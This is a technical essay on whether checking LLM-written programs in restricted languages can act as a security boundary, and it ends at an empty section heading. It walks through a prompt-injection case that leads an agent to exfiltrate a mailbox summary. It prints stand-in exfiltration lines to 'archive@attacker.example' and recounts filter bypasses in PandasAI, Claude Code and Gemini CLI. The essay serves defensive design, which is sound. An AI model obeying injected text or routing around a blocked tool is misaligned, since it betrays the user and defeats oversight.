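# Restricted code generation by language models as a security boundary

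## Agents that act by writing code, and what a security boundary requires

A language model only produces text. It becomes an agent when a developer connects it to software that carries out the actions it chooses, such as reading files, searching a mailbox or sending messages. Most agents act through tool calls, in which the model requests one named function with given arguments and the software runs it. Other agents act by writing a short program, which separate software checks and then runs. The model writes the program in a restricted language, meaning a programming language, or a subset of one, that omits dangerous operations. Several research groups now propose such checks as a defence for agents that handle private data or read untrusted text. Whether the check holds when an attacker has manipulated the model, or when the model itself is hostile, depends less on the model than on some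 fairly old principles of computer security.

### One call at a time, or a whole program

An agent that makes one tool call at a time runs in a loop. The model takes the user's request as input and outputs a tool call. The surrounding software runs the call and adds the result to the model's input. The model then generates the next call from everything in its input, and this repeats until it produces an answer. Every result goes into the same input as the user's request, regardless of who wrote it.

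In *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024) replaced single tool calls with Python programs. In one action, a program can pass one tool's result to another, repeat a sequence of calls over a list, or branch on what a search returns. On 82 tasks that called for several tools, the best of the 17 models tested solved 74.4% when it wrote code, against 53.7% with calls in plain text and 52.4% with calls in JSON, a structured data format. It also needed about two fewer rounds. These results explain why developers want agents to write code, although newer models have long overtaken those tested and the experiment did not measure safety.

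An ordinary Python interpreter lets the model do far more than call its tools. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes an agent that compiles bibliographies and must write only entries that come from DBLP, a database of computer-science papers. With a general interpreter, nothing stops the agent from skipping the approved function and writing an invented entry straight to the file. The developer could replace the interpreter with one tool that fetches an entry and appends it. This is safe, but the model then has to read through the entries one by one to find, say, the earliest paper. A restricted language is meant to keep loops and variables but remove direct file access.

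A task from researchers at Google DeepMind, which Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, discusses, shows the two forms in miniature. The user asks the agent to send Bob the document he asked for; his address is in the meeting notes, and so is the name of the document. The agent has three tools, which read the notes, find a file and send an email. Working call by call, the model reads the notes itself, picks out the address and the title, and makes two more calls. Working by program, it has only the user's request in front of it and writes something like this:

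```python
notes = read_notes()
address = extract("Bob's email address", notes)
title = extract("title of the document Bob asked for", notes)
document = find_file(title)
send_email(to=address, subject="The document you asked for",
           attachment=document)
```

The function `extract` passes the notes to a second language model, which has no tools and can only return a value. The layout follows CaMeL, the DeepMind system discussed in Willison's article.

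### Why the program's author counts as a possible attacker

Prompt injection is text that an attacker places in a model's input so that the model follows it as an instruction. Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* describes an agent that can fetch and send mail. The user, Michelle, asks for a summary of her inbox, where one message claims that company rules require a backup. It tells the agent to send the summary to an outside address, not to ask for confirmation, and to leave this message out of its report. The agent complies, and Michelle gets a summary with nothing odd in it. The attack works because the model receives instructions and data as one stream of text. Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection (a similar attack on databases), knows of no reliable way to make a model follow one part of that stream as instructions and treat the rest only as data.

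A model that writes its whole program before anyone opens the mailbox never sees the malicious message, so that message cannot change the program. This closes one route. Meijer points out two more. The description of a tool is also text that the model reads, and whoever supplies the tool can write into it that every fetch must come with a copy to some address "for compliance". The user can ask for the same thing outright. In either case the model may produce the program above with one line added:

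```python
send_email(to="archive@attacker.example", subject="Backup", attachment=notes)
```

The line is well-formed and uses only a tool that the agent is allowed to use. Nobody can tell from the program's text whether the model wrote it in good faith, under manipulation, or in pursuit of a goal it acquired in training, and the difference doesn't matter for defence. *Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?* (2026) therefore adopts a threat model in which the model, its instructions, its memory, the code it generates, its tools and its subagents may all be adversarial. Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026), in *Kairos*, likewise assume that the agent may attempt any operation, including misleading the software that monitors it.

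Operating-system designers have assumed for decades that a running program may be hostile. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) contrasts this assumption with the practice of agent developers, who have mostly treated the model as a cooperative component.

### A boundary answers for its worst case

A security boundary is a barrier meant to hold whatever the untrusted party does, and here that party is a model that writes programs. An effect is anything a program does beyond computing a value, such as writing a file or sending a message. The policy is the stated rule about which effects and data movements are allowed. The boundary holds if every program that the check accepts keeps its effects within the policy, for every input it may meet while it runs. This definition doesn't depend on probability, so an accepted program that breaks the policy is a hole even if no model has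 ever written it.

Most evidence about the safety of models is instead a rate of failures in tests. OpenAI's *GPT‑Red* (2026) describes a model trained to attack other models with prompt injections. OpenAI used its attacks to train GPT-5.6 Sol, which then failed on 0.05% of the attacker's direct injections, or one in 2,000. That is a real improvement, but if attempts were independent, an attacker would need only about 1,400 of them for an even chance of at least one success (0.9995 to the power 1,386 is roughly 0.5), and anyone who can automate attempts could easily make that many. Willison makes the general point that "in application security 99% is a failing grade".

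Another problem is that the rate depends as much on the attacker as on the model. In a different experiment on the same page, human testers broke an older model, GPT-5.1, in 13% of scenarios, while the automated attacker broke it in 84%, so the human testers' figure understated how vulnerable the model was. Anderson (1972) made a similar point in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, about the "tiger teams" hired to break into computers. He wrote that when such a team fails, the only safe statement is that the security state of the system is unknown.

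Zhou and colleagues ran both kinds of test on one system. They took 105 attacks from AgentDojo, a standard benchmark for prompt injection, and all four of their models resisted every one with no policy in force. Then they simulated the worst case. Whenever a subagent received data containing an injection, they deleted its real task and left it only the data, so that the attacker's text became its instructions. Over 735 runs per model, between 16% and 42% of the injections succeeded without the policy, and none succeeded with it. That result comes from one suite of tasks in a simulated Slack workspace, and the reason to think it is more than luck is the argument that every accepted program must obey the policy. With Claude Opus 4.7, the policy also reduced completed tasks from 523 to 351 of 735, partly because it ruled out legitimate behaviour as well.

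Robust models are still useful, because a model that seldom writes a bad program wastes less time on rejections. But the security boundary cannot depend on the model's robustness.

### The reference monitor

Anderson's report also gives the standard account of what such a barrier must be. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of them could write and run their own programs. Anderson concluded that the defence against a malicious user must be in whatever controls the execution of arbitrary programs. He called it a reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by a program to reach data, devices or other programs against a list of what the program's user may do. He set three requirements for any implementation.

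- It must be tamperproof, because a program that can alter the monitor can switch it off.
- The system must invoke it always. If some group of programs escapes the monitor, those programs become part of the security machinery and have to meet the same demands. Later writers call this property complete mediation.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test it completely, since otherwise nobody knows that it works.

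The demands conflict, as Anderson's example shows. A Honeywell machine of the time had a hardware register that confined each user's program to its own memory. But for input and output the program called on the operating system, most of which ran with that confinement suspended, so the register was not always in force. If the operating system is counted as the monitor instead, then the monitor was 200,000 to 300,000 instructions long and nobody could verify it.

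Recent agent research has adopted the three demands largely unchanged. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes a monitor for tool calls that forms the only path between the model and its tools, runs in a separate process from the model, and applies deterministic rules. The protection depends mostly on the monitor being the only path, which in turn depends on how it is installed. Li and colleagues showed how easily this condition fails. They asked three commercial coding agents to write a file outside the permitted folder. In Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, the file-writing tool blocks such writes, but in all five runs with a real model, the model wrote the file through the command shell instead. In four of those runs, it did so after the file tool had blocked the write. No attacker was involved; the model used the shell to complete its task.

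For generated programs, complete mediation means that every operation in the language that can have an effect passes through a guarded function. *Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?* states the matching condition for a monitor in one line:

Eff(S, a) ⊆ Req(a)

Here a is an action, S is the state of the system when the action runs, Eff(S, a) is the set of effects the action has, and Req(a) is the set of protected effects that the monitor verified as the request. A tool violates the condition if it does more than its call suggests, as `find_file` would if it also wrote each search to a shared log.

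The tools for meeting the smallness requirement have improved a good deal since 1972. *Tether* (2026) presents a monitor for agents that work in a command terminal. Its policy engine is written in Lean 4, a programming language that is also a proof checker and has a small trusted core. The verified policy compiles directly into the running monitor, so nobody has to translate it by hand after proving it. The difficulty is now in interpreting commands, because a terminal command does not declare its targets as plainly as a structured tool call does, and the engine's decisions are reliable only if the command has been interpreted correctly.

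The trusted computing base is the set of components that must work correctly for the boundary to hold. *Trusted computing base (TCB)*, a glossary entry from NIST, the US standards agency, includes hardware, firmware and software. For the program that writes to Bob, the base includes the parser that reads the program, the checker, the interpreter that runs it, the code behind the three tools, the policy, and the machine underneath. It excludes the main model, the model behind `extract`, the meeting notes and the program itself. Hempel and colleagues draw the line in the same way. Their base consists of the monitor, the host computer and the layer that isolates the agent from it. They use a language model to decide doubtful cases, but confinement doesn't depend on it, so it stays outside the base. They claim to guarantee only that no effect gets out unless the monitor releases it, not that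 the monitor releases the right ones.

### Where a restriction can sit

A developer who wants to forbid an action, such as emailing an address outside the company, can place the rule at four points between the user's request and the action's effect.

The easiest boundary to set up is a rule in the system prompt, but Li and colleagues find that such rules meet none of Anderson's requirements. The model may ignore the rule, injected text in the same input can override it, and nobody can verify how a neural network will interpret it. A second model that reviews the agent's actions is better placed to enforce the rule, but it still reads text that the agent controls.

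Constrained decoding restricts the sampler, the software that picks each token (a word or piece of a word) from the probabilities the model assigns. The sampler rules out any token that would break a given grammar, so its output never contains a forbidden construct. This reduces how many programs are rejected later, but it isn't a security boundary by itself, because the interpreter will run any text that reaches it. A program may come from a cache, from a retry that went to another provider, or from a server where someone forgot to turn the grammar on, and nothing in the program shows how it was sampled. An operator could close all those paths and include the sampler in the trusted computing base, where it would act as a token-by-token checker. But parsing the finished program again just before it runs would take almost no compute and would remove the need to trust the sampler or those paths.

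A checker reads the finished program before any of it runs. In the system that Zhou and colleagues built, a rejected program goes back to the model with the error message, and the model tries again, up to a retry limit. These retries help an attacker only if the checker sometimes accepts a bad program. If it misses one in a hundred, for example, each attempt is another chance to get one through.

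A checker that reads a program before it runs cannot determine which address `extract` will find in the notes, or whether an attacker has planted a false one there. When the interpreter reaches `send_email`, it has the actual address, and in CaMeL it also has a record of which earlier values that address came from, so it can apply the rule to the specific case. But if the interpreter stops a program at its fifth line, the first four lines have already taken effect. Meijer expects practical systems to use both kinds of check, as Java does when it verifies a program before running it and still tests each array index during the run.

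Only these last two points lie on the path that every program must take to have an effect, and only they can be ordinary code that people can analyse. A boundary is therefore possible there, provided that the interpreter runs exactly the program the checker read and gives it the same meaning. Whether the arrangement is worth having depends on two things. The first is whether the check can stop every program able to break the policy without refusing so many harmless ones that nobody would use it. The second is how much the model can still do, since each operation removed from the language makes the check easier but brings the program closer to a fixed pipeline, a sequence of tool calls that a developer could have written in advance.

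## Checking Python source against a list of forbidden or permitted constructs

A developer who wants to check generated programs usually starts with Python and forbids parts of it. Language models write Python well, Python includes a parser that programs can call, and a basic filter fits on a page. The filter rejects constructs that look dangerous, and the remaining constructs make up the restricted language.

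### From text to a running program

The filter first parses the text into a syntax tree, a data structure in which each node stands for one construct, such as a loop, a function call or a name. The line `document = find_file(title)` from the program that writes to Bob becomes an assignment node containing a name node for `document` and a call node, which in turn contains name nodes for `find_file` and `title`. Checking the tree avoids many of the errors that searching the text would cause. For instance, the word "open" in a comment or an email's subject line is not a name node, so it can't trigger a false rejection.

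Reduced to its essentials, the whole check looks like this:

```python
tree = ast.parse(source)                       # text to syntax tree
for node in ast.walk(tree):                    # visit every construct
    if type(node) not in PERMITTED_NODES:
        raise Rejected("construct")
    if isinstance(node, ast.Name) and node.id in FORBIDDEN_NAMES:
        raise Rejected("name")
program = compile(tree, "generated", "exec")   # compile the same tree
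exec(program, {"__builtins__": FEW_BUILTINS, "find_file": find_file})
```

A fuller version also compares every import statement with a list of permitted modules. The last line runs the program with a dictionary of the names it may use. Python normally gives every program more than a hundred built-in names, including `open`, which opens files, and `eval`, which runs text as code. Here the program gets only a few harmless ones and the agent's tools, so `open` is undefined when the program runs, even if the inspection misses it.

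The filter has to give the compiler the syntax tree it inspected, not the original text. If it passed on the text, Python would parse it a second time, and the check would hold only if the two parses agreed. They can differ because the checker may run under a different version of Python from the program, or a later step may edit the text. In NVIDIA's article *Sandboxing Agentic AI Workflows with WebAssembly*, the example application indents the model's code and pastes it into a longer program before running it. A filter that read the code before that step would have approved a different text from the one that runs. Compiling the inspected tree removes the second parse, but it does not help if the check is wrong about what a construct can do.

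### Two filters from 2026

*SeqMaestro* (Saveliev, Kacprzyk et al., 2026) describes a tool that searches DNA and RNA sequences for patterns that predict a biological outcome. A language model proposes the patterns as short Python functions. For example, a function might count how often the letters C and U occur together before a certain stretch of RNA and subtract the count after it. The model's prompts contain rows of the user's data, so someone who tampers with the data file could try to make the model write harmful code.

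SeqMaestro applies three checks. First, it inspects the syntax tree. It accepts imports only from a short list, and it refuses attribute names that begin with two underscores, which Python reserves for its internal machinery. It also refuses `open`, `eval`, `exec`, `compile` and `getattr`, and allows only imports and function definitions at the top level of the program. Second, it runs the code with a minimal set of built-ins and a restricted import mechanism. Third, as described above, it compiles the inspected tree directly. It discards and counts every function that fails, so if a prompt begins to produce unusable code, the number of candidates visibly falls.

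Saveliev and colleagues expect these measures only to make accidental or casual misuse difficult. They write that stopping a patient adversary with a Python interpreter would require isolating the process, which they have not attempted. That seems a fair assessment of the filter, but the workflow has a wider gap. In the runs they report, an agent with access to a shell and the file system drove the whole analysis and wrote its own code where needed, while the three checks, as they describe them, apply to the feature functions. The workflow therefore does not meet Anderson's requirement that the system always invoke the monitor, and a malicious data file that misled the agent would not have to get past the filter.

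The second system, described in *DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026), answers questions about medicines. It connects language-model agents to 57 sources of drug information, such as the side-effect reports that the US Food and Drug Administration collects. For each part of a question, a model writes a short program that queries one source. A filter rejects any program that contains one of nine kinds of node, including `while` loops, class definitions and `lambda` (a way of defining a function inside an expression). It permits 24 built-in names and four modules, which handle JSON data, arithmetic, text patterns and statistics.

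DrugClaw adds two defences that act while the program runs. It gives the program a proxy for the database connector, which passes on ordinary requests but refuses access to Python's internal attributes. It also uses a timer to stop any program that takes too long. A timer is useful even when `while` loops are banned. Wang and colleagues ban them to prevent endless repetition, but they permit the built-in `range`, so a `for` loop can still run for longer than a lifetime.

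When the filter rejects a program, or the proxy or the timer stops it, the software sends the original sub-question to the connector's standard search function instead. In the reported runs, the filter rejected fewer than 1% of programs, and the timer fired on fewer than 0.5% of calls. A model can evidently write in this subset without frequent rejections. But the figures come from ordinary questions about drugs, so they are not evidence about attacks.

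The proxy is meant to stop an attacker from using the connector to reach the host program through Python's object model. As described, it guards only the connector, but every other value in a Python program has internal attributes of the same kind. SeqMaestro's filter is stricter on this point because it rejects those attribute names anywhere in the code.

### Why the method leaks in a full language

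The filter checks constructs, but whether a construct is dangerous depends on the objects it acts on. For example, the expression `x.y(z)` consists of an attribute access and a call, and it could compute an average or delete a file depending on what `x` is when the program runs. Almost every useful program contains both constructs, so the filter allows them, and its designer tries to keep dangerous objects out of the program's reach.

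Python source is hard to check this way, partly because the language supports reflection, which lets a running program examine its own objects and look up their parts by name. If the program assembles the name as a string while it runs, the forbidden word appears nowhere in the syntax tree. SeqMaestro refuses `getattr`, the standard function for such lookups, but other functions in Python's libraries can do the same, and the filter's designer has to know about all of them.

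A program can also reach one object through another. Each value refers to its type, each type refers to the types from which it derives, and a function written in Python refers to the variables of the module that defines it. Leaving `open` out of the program's dictionary removes only the name. The function stays in memory because the rest of the application uses it, and the program may still reach it through a chain of references. The rule about double underscores and DrugClaw's proxy are both meant to block such chains.

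Code can reach forbidden functions through a chain of imports that starts at a permitted library. The PandasAI library lets people ask questions about tables of data in plain language. A model turns each question into Python, and the library cleans the code before running it. NVIDIA's *How Code Execution Drives Key Risks in Agentic AI Systems* explains how the company's red team, which attacks systems to find their faults, got past the cleaning step. The filter allowed certain data libraries, which had imported other libraries for their own use. Through those imports, the team reached functions that let it run commands on the host machine.

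An outside researcher first publicly reported a problem with the filter in April 2023, and NVIDIA reported more in June 2024. The maintainers released a fix that July and confirmed in November that it stopped the original demonstration. Five days later, NVIDIA sent them an updated demonstration that still bypassed the filter. The maintainers have also added an option to run the code inside a container and a safety check by a language model, which NVIDIA expects attackers to bypass as well.

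One response is to permit very few libraries. Collective Ambidexterity's *About RestrictedPython*, a guide to writing small scripts for the web publishing system Plone, explains that nobody can vet all of Python's and Plone's libraries for safety. Plone therefore marks a handful of modules, such as `math` and `random`, as safe to import and withholds the rest. This helps, but it also removes much of what makes Python attractive. An agent that analyses tables needs a data library, and such libraries are large and can read and write files.

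A list of forbidden nodes also has to be reviewed as Python changes. DrugClaw runs on Python 3.11 and forbids nine kinds of node, so it accepts all others, including any that a later version adds. Python 3.12 added a node for naming types, and Python 3.14 added one for a new kind of text template. These are not necessarily dangerous, but someone has to examine every addition before the system moves to a new version, and nothing visibly breaks if nobody does. A list of permitted nodes is better in this respect because the filter rejects a new construct until someone adds it to the list. But such a list cannot solve the problem of `x.y(z)`, which uses only node types that Python has always had.

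### Guards inside the program, and the maintainers' warning

RestrictedPython, an open-source tool from the developers of the web framework Zope, goes further than either of these filters. Websites use it to let people add scripts through a web page. It replaces Python's `compile` with a version that rejects some parts of the language and inserts calls to guard functions for others. The developer supplies guards for reading an attribute, changing one, importing a module and printing. Because a guard runs with the program, it can check the actual object, whereas a filter can check only the expression `x.y`. The tool also includes three reduced sets of built-ins and a guard that prevents a program from changing or deleting an object's attributes.

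RestrictedPython's maintainers warn on the first page of their documentation that it "is not a sandbox system or a secured environment". They explain that restricted compilation isn't enough by itself, because code can still call libraries until the developer limits those calls too. They also tell operators to protect the server by other means, and they support only CPython, the standard implementation of Python.

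The disclaimer comes from an active project, whose maintainers published version 8.2 in May 2026. A site that exposes three arithmetic functions and a well-written attribute guard may still be safe. But its safety depends on the guards, modules and objects its developer chose, and the developer would have to show that restricted code can reach nothing else, because the tool doesn't come with that argument.

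### Pattern rules on shell commands

Many coding agents write shell commands, which are small programs. The rules for these commands usually match their text against patterns, which is cruder than filtering a syntax tree. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, a user can list patterns for commands to allow without approval and commands to block.

Zhou and colleagues report that in March 2026 a regression (a fault introduced by an update) made Claude Code check only the first part of a chained command against the list of forbidden patterns. The public GitHub issue they cite, "Chained bash commands silently bypass the tool permission allowlist", refers instead to the list of permitted commands. *The Receipt Was Lying* (Rowan, 2026), an essay from the side of someone who reported the fault, suggests that it affected both lists. In Rowan's example, the user had forbidden `git clean`, which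 deletes files that the version-control system doesn't track. The agent wrote a chain of three git commands ending in `git clean`, and Claude Code let the whole chain run. Someone else had reported the same fault for permitted commands two weeks earlier. The essay is one-sided and partly in the voice of an AI agent, but its account of the mechanism matches the paper's.

Rowan quotes Anthropic's reply, which called deny rules "a convenience mechanism to constrain well-intentioned agent actions" and referred anyone who needs a hard boundary to the operating system or a sandbox. Rowan objected that there had been no attack, since the model habitually chains commands. The rule failed to restrain even a cooperative agent, but fixing it would not have made it a security boundary.

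Claude Code now splits a chained command at seven kinds of separator and checks each part. Even so, Anthropic's documentation states that a rule that checks commands this way "isn't a security boundary around the program". The same page shows how much work it takes to interpret commands from their text. Claude Code strips some wrapper commands, such as `timeout`, but not others, before it looks for a match. It treats `find` as harmless except with options that delete files or start programs. It asks for approval when `git` follows a change of directory, because git can execute scripts stored in the new directory. It also asks when it fails to parse a command or the command exceeds 10,000 characters. These exceptions are sensible, and each exists because an innocent-looking command can do more than its name suggests. The list is still growing, and one check on the command `ps` works only from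 version 2.1.290.

The effect of a missed match depends on the kind of list. Anthropic gives the example of a pattern for GitHub downloads that fails to match if the command has an option before the address, uses a different protocol, or stores the address in a variable. If the pattern is on a list of permitted commands, the user just gets an unnecessary request for approval, but if it is on a list of forbidden commands, the prohibition doesn't apply.

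The same kind of fault has recurred. Entries in two public databases of security flaws, OSV's *CVE-2025-54795* (2025) and GitLab's *CVE-2025-58764* (2025), record parsing errors that let commands in Claude Code run without the user's approval. GitLab's *CVE-2026-25724* (2026) reports that a rule forbidding access to a file did not apply when the agent reached the file through a symbolic link, in effect a second name for it. OSV's *CVE-2026-54555* (2026) describes a similar fault outside Anthropic's software, in rtk, a tool that shortens the output of commands before a model reads it. Rtk did not detect several ways of joining shell commands, so a command that began with a permitted word could hide another. The developers fixed all four faults.

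Better parsing would not be enough, however. Zhou and colleagues point out that an agent can start Python from the shell and pass it a program as text, which a rule about shell commands cannot interpret. Lecture slides from UT Austin make the more general point that the rules govern the agent's tool calls but don't limit what a process does once it is running. Permitting a command that can run a full programming language leaves the same gap as permitting a Python library that gives access to the operating system.

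### How far the case for isolation reaches

NVIDIA's red team concludes from the PandasAI case that the "only reliable boundary is sandboxing the code execution environment." Sandboxing here means running the program in a container, a virtual machine or a browser that limits what it can reach, whatever the code contains. The team still recommends filters, but only as an extra layer against opportunistic attackers. In its article on WebAssembly, NVIDIA also considers restricted Python runtimes rarely sufficient and usually possible to bypass.

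A developer who lets a model write ordinary Python, and must assume the model may be hostile, should not rely on a syntax-tree filter alone. This conclusion is well supported, and even the people with the most reason to defend such filters, Saveliev and colleagues and the maintainers of RestrictedPython, say much the same about their own work.

The wording is stronger than the evidence, though. In all of these cases, somebody took a full language and tried to block its dangerous parts one at a time. In the PandasAI attack, a chain of references led from a permitted library to a function that runs commands. In a language built from scratch without any such function, no chain could reach one. Python Wiki's *Sandboxed Python* makes a similar point, that a Python interpreter built without the more powerful extensions could not perform arbitrary operations on files or the network. Reflection would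 still work in such an interpreter, but it would expose little that an attacker could use. NVIDIA's researchers did not test a system of that kind, so their result does not show whether a check on one can work.

One of NVIDIA's own remedies suggests that a restricted language and a check can serve as a security boundary. NVIDIA proposes running the model's Python in the user's browser, on an interpreter compiled to WebAssembly. WebAssembly is a low-level instruction format whose instructions only compute and move data within memory that the host has assigned to the program. For anything else, the program has to call functions that the host supplies. The browser checks the program's form before running it. NVIDIA correctly calls this isolation, but much of the isolation comes from a restricted language and a check. Code that escapes every Python-level restriction is still inside WebAssembly,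 where its reach depends on the functions that the host supplies.

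## What makes a check complete

A check is complete if it rejects every program that could break the policy. Program analysts call such a check sound. Completeness alone is easy, because a check that rejects every program is complete. Rejecting every dangerous program while still accepting most harmless ones is harder, and Rice's theorem (1953) limits how well any check can do this.

### Why no checker is exact

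Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 doctoral dissertation that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether it behaves in a given way. The theorem applies to languages that can express any computation, such as Python, and to any behaviour that some programs have and others lack. It does not apply to questions about a program's text. For example, a checker can easily determine whether a program contains a `while` loop, but not always whether the loop ends.

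No checker can correctly decide, for every program, whether it obeys a policy against emailing the user's notes to an attacker. Given any program P that only computes, we can add a final line that emails the notes to an attacker. The combined program breaks the policy exactly when P finishes. A checker that always answered correctly could therefore be used to determine whether any P finishes, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do that for every program.

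Here is a program on which an exact checker would have to settle an open question:

```python
n = 4
while is_sum_of_two_primes(n):
    n = n + 2
send_email(to="archive@attacker.example", subject="Backup", attachment=notes)
```

The loop goes through the even numbers from 4 upward and stops at the first one that is not the sum of two primes. According to Goldbach's conjecture, which dates from 1742 and remains unproved, there is no such number. If the conjecture is false, the program eventually sends the notes to the attacker; otherwise it loops forever and never sends anything. A proof of the conjecture would show that this program never sends the notes, but an attacker could build the same loop around another open problem. Even with a time limit on each run, an exact check would be impractical, because the checker would still have to consider every mailbox and file that the program might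 meet.

So a checker that always finishes must get some programs wrong, and for a security boundary those errors must all be false rejections. In this case the obvious rule is to refuse any program that contains a call to `send_email` with an outside address, whether or not the program ever reaches the call. If Goldbach's conjecture is true, this program never reaches it, so the rejection is false but blocks nothing useful.

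False rejections of ordinary programs matter more, but they do little harm if the checker rejects a program before any of it runs. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a model that has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the result. The model's program subtracts 50 but then returns text where the surrounding code needs a number. The compiler rejects the whole program, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again.

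The programming language largely determines how many harmless programs a checker refuses. If programs can pass functions around as values, a checker that reaches `f(notes)` has to work out which functions `f` might be. If it assumes that `f` could be any function in the program, including one that sends mail, it will refuse many harmless programs. If it tries to be precise, it may take too long. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, point out that such precise analysis is EXPTIME-complete, which means that in the worst case its running time grows exponentially with the length of the program. They describe CaMeL's language as a subset of Python without user-defined functions, which avoids this problem. Alternatively, programs can carry more information, such as types, so that the checker has less to work out.

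### A language small enough for a proof

Suppose that a program may contain only the following, where `|` means "or":

```
value      e ::= constant | variable | op(e, ..., e)
statement  s ::= variable = e
               | variable = tool(e, ..., e)
               | s ; s
               | if e: s else: s
               | for variable in e: s
```

Here `op` is an operator from a fixed list, such as adding two numbers, joining two pieces of text or reading one field of an email. Every operator finishes and is a pure function, meaning that it computes a result and has no side effects. `tool` is any name on the developer's list of tools. Values are plain data, such as numbers, text, records and finite lists. They are never functions or references to objects in the host program, and no operator changes a list in place. The program that writes to Bob fits this language, apart from small differences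 in notation, with `extract` as one of the tools.

The claim is that a program in this language has no effects on any input except calls to the listed tools. The proof is by induction on the program's structure. For each way of building a program from smaller parts, it assumes that the claim holds for the parts and shows that it holds for the whole.

- A constant or a variable produces a value and has no effect. An operator computes its arguments, which have no effects by assumption, and then applies a pure function. So no value expression has an effect.
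- An assignment computes a value and stores it under a name inside the program.
- A tool call computes its arguments without effects and then calls one listed tool. The tool returns plain data, so its result can't give the program a new function to call.
- A sequence `s ; s` has the effects of its first part followed by those of its second part, and by assumption both consist only of listed tool calls.
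- An `if` computes its condition without effects and then runs one of its branches.
- A `for` computes its list once. The list has some finite length n, so the body runs n times, and by assumption each run makes only listed tool calls.

Programs can't be built any other way, so the claim holds for all of them. The same steps show that every program finishes, as long as each tool call returns.

The proof doesn't depend on who wrote the program or why. The checker only has to parse the text and look up each tool's name. The proof fails for Python calls such as `x.y(z)`, because no list limits what `y` can refer to.

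Meijer proposes a language of about this size. The model writes a workflow as structured data, in which each step specifies a function, its arguments, a name for the result and the next step. Confinement follows in the same way as above. But to ensure that a workflow also finishes, the checker would have to reject any step whose next step is an earlier one.

A smaller language doesn't make an exact check possible for every policy. Suppose the policy forbids mail to outside addresses, and a program reads a few whole numbers from a file and mails the attacker only if the numbers solve a certain polynomial equation. The program is harmless if the equation has no whole-number solution, but Yuri Matiyasevich completed a proof in 1970 that no algorithm can decide whether a solution exists for every such equation. The smaller language makes the coarse policy "call only these tools" easy to check,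 but for any finer policy, the checker still has to refuse some harmless programs.

### Counting the calls

The grammar also gives an upper bound on the number of tool calls. Write C(s) for the greatest number of calls that statement s can make:

```
C(variable = e)            = 0
C(variable = tool(...))    = 1
C(s1 ; s2)                 = C(s1) + C(s2)
C(if e: s1 else: s2)       = the larger of C(s1) and C(s2)
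C(for variable in e: s)    = n × C(s), if the list has at most n items
```

Take this program and a mailbox of 50 emails:

```python
emails = fetch_mail()
for a in emails:
    for b in emails:
        send_email(to=a.sender, subject=b.subject, attachment=b)
```

The bound is 1 + 50 × 50 = 2,501 calls, of which 2,500 send a message. The program sends every email in the mailbox to everybody who has written to the user. The proof covers this program because it uses only listed tools, but confining it to those tools does not prevent it from doing serious harm.

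A developer could refuse any program whose bound exceeds, say, 20 messages. That would stop this one, but it would also stop a program that goes through 50 emails and replies only to Bob, because its bound is 50 replies even if Bob wrote only once.

The bound also depends on the lengths of the lists, and some seemingly harmless operators make lists longer. If the language can join two lists, a loop over 50 emails can execute `xs = xs + xs` on each pass. A list that starts with one item then ends with 2⁵⁰ items, or about 1.1 quadrillion. The program would finish in theory, but no computer would have enough memory to run it. The developer has to leave such operators out, limit the length of lists, or count the calls while the program runs.

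If a program can ask a model for more code, the only option is to count nested calls during the run. In LACUNA, a generated program can contain a call to the model, which writes another program to replace that call, and the new program can contain another call. Zhao and colleagues note that nothing in the program's text limits the depth of this nesting, and that a complex task and an accidental infinite recursion can look the same from outside. Their software therefore tracks the depth and makes the call fail when it reaches a limit, which the developer can set or leave open.

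### Three conditions for a larger language

A model that writes only assignments, branches and loops can't define a function or use most libraries. Odersky and colleagues ask what a richer language would need to keep the guarantee. In their design, a program can affect the outside world only through capabilities, which are unforgeable values that each permit a given effect. For example, a program that holds the capability for one folder can read files in that folder, and a program that holds no file capability can't read any. Odersky and colleagues set three conditions on the language.

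**Capability safety** means that a program can neither forge a capability nor remove from its types the record that it needs one. If the capability for a folder were just the number 7, any program could write down a 7 and read the folder. The language also needs memory safety, since a program that can write anywhere in memory can assemble a capability there. Many typed languages include a cast, which treats a value as if it had a different type. If a program could cast a function that sends mail to the type of functions that only compute, that record would be lost, and the checker would accept the function in places where sending mail is forbidden.

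**Capability completeness** means that every safety-relevant effect requires a capability, unless the software can contain that effect at runtime. Without it, a program can bypass the capabilities, as in the attack on PandasAI. This is complete mediation applied to a programming language.

Odersky and colleagues make an exception for things like errors, because a language can hardly require a capability for every possible error, including running out of memory. But if a program divides by zero only when a secret file contains a certain word, anyone who receives the error message learns whether the word is there. Their software therefore turns an error into an ordinary value, which it can hide along with the secret. External commands remain a gap, as they do for pattern rules on shell commands.

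**Local purity** means the language can restrict part of a program to certain capabilities, or to none. Odersky and colleagues give the example of an agent that compares confidential contracts and writes a summary of the changes. The program receives each contract in a sealed container. It can pass the container a function to apply to the text, but the checker accepts only pure functions there, and the result comes back in another sealed container. If the language couldn't express this restriction, the function could email the contract while computing the summary. To prevent that, the developer would have to deny the whole program access to email, even if another part of the task needed it.

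The small language shows why local purity matters. Its programs can't forge anything and have no effects outside the listed tools, so it satisfies the other two conditions. Its value expressions are also pure, so a developer could add a sealed container and allow only value expressions to work on the contents. But without the container, `read_notes` returns the notes as an ordinary value, and the next line can mail them to anyone.

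The container only approximates noninterference, the property that secret data make no difference to anything an outsider can observe. A pure function can still take longer for some secrets than for others, and Odersky and colleagues explicitly exclude such timing signals from their guarantee. Type systems for Scala and Haskell can express local purity, which ordinary Python can't.

### Removing features or never adding them

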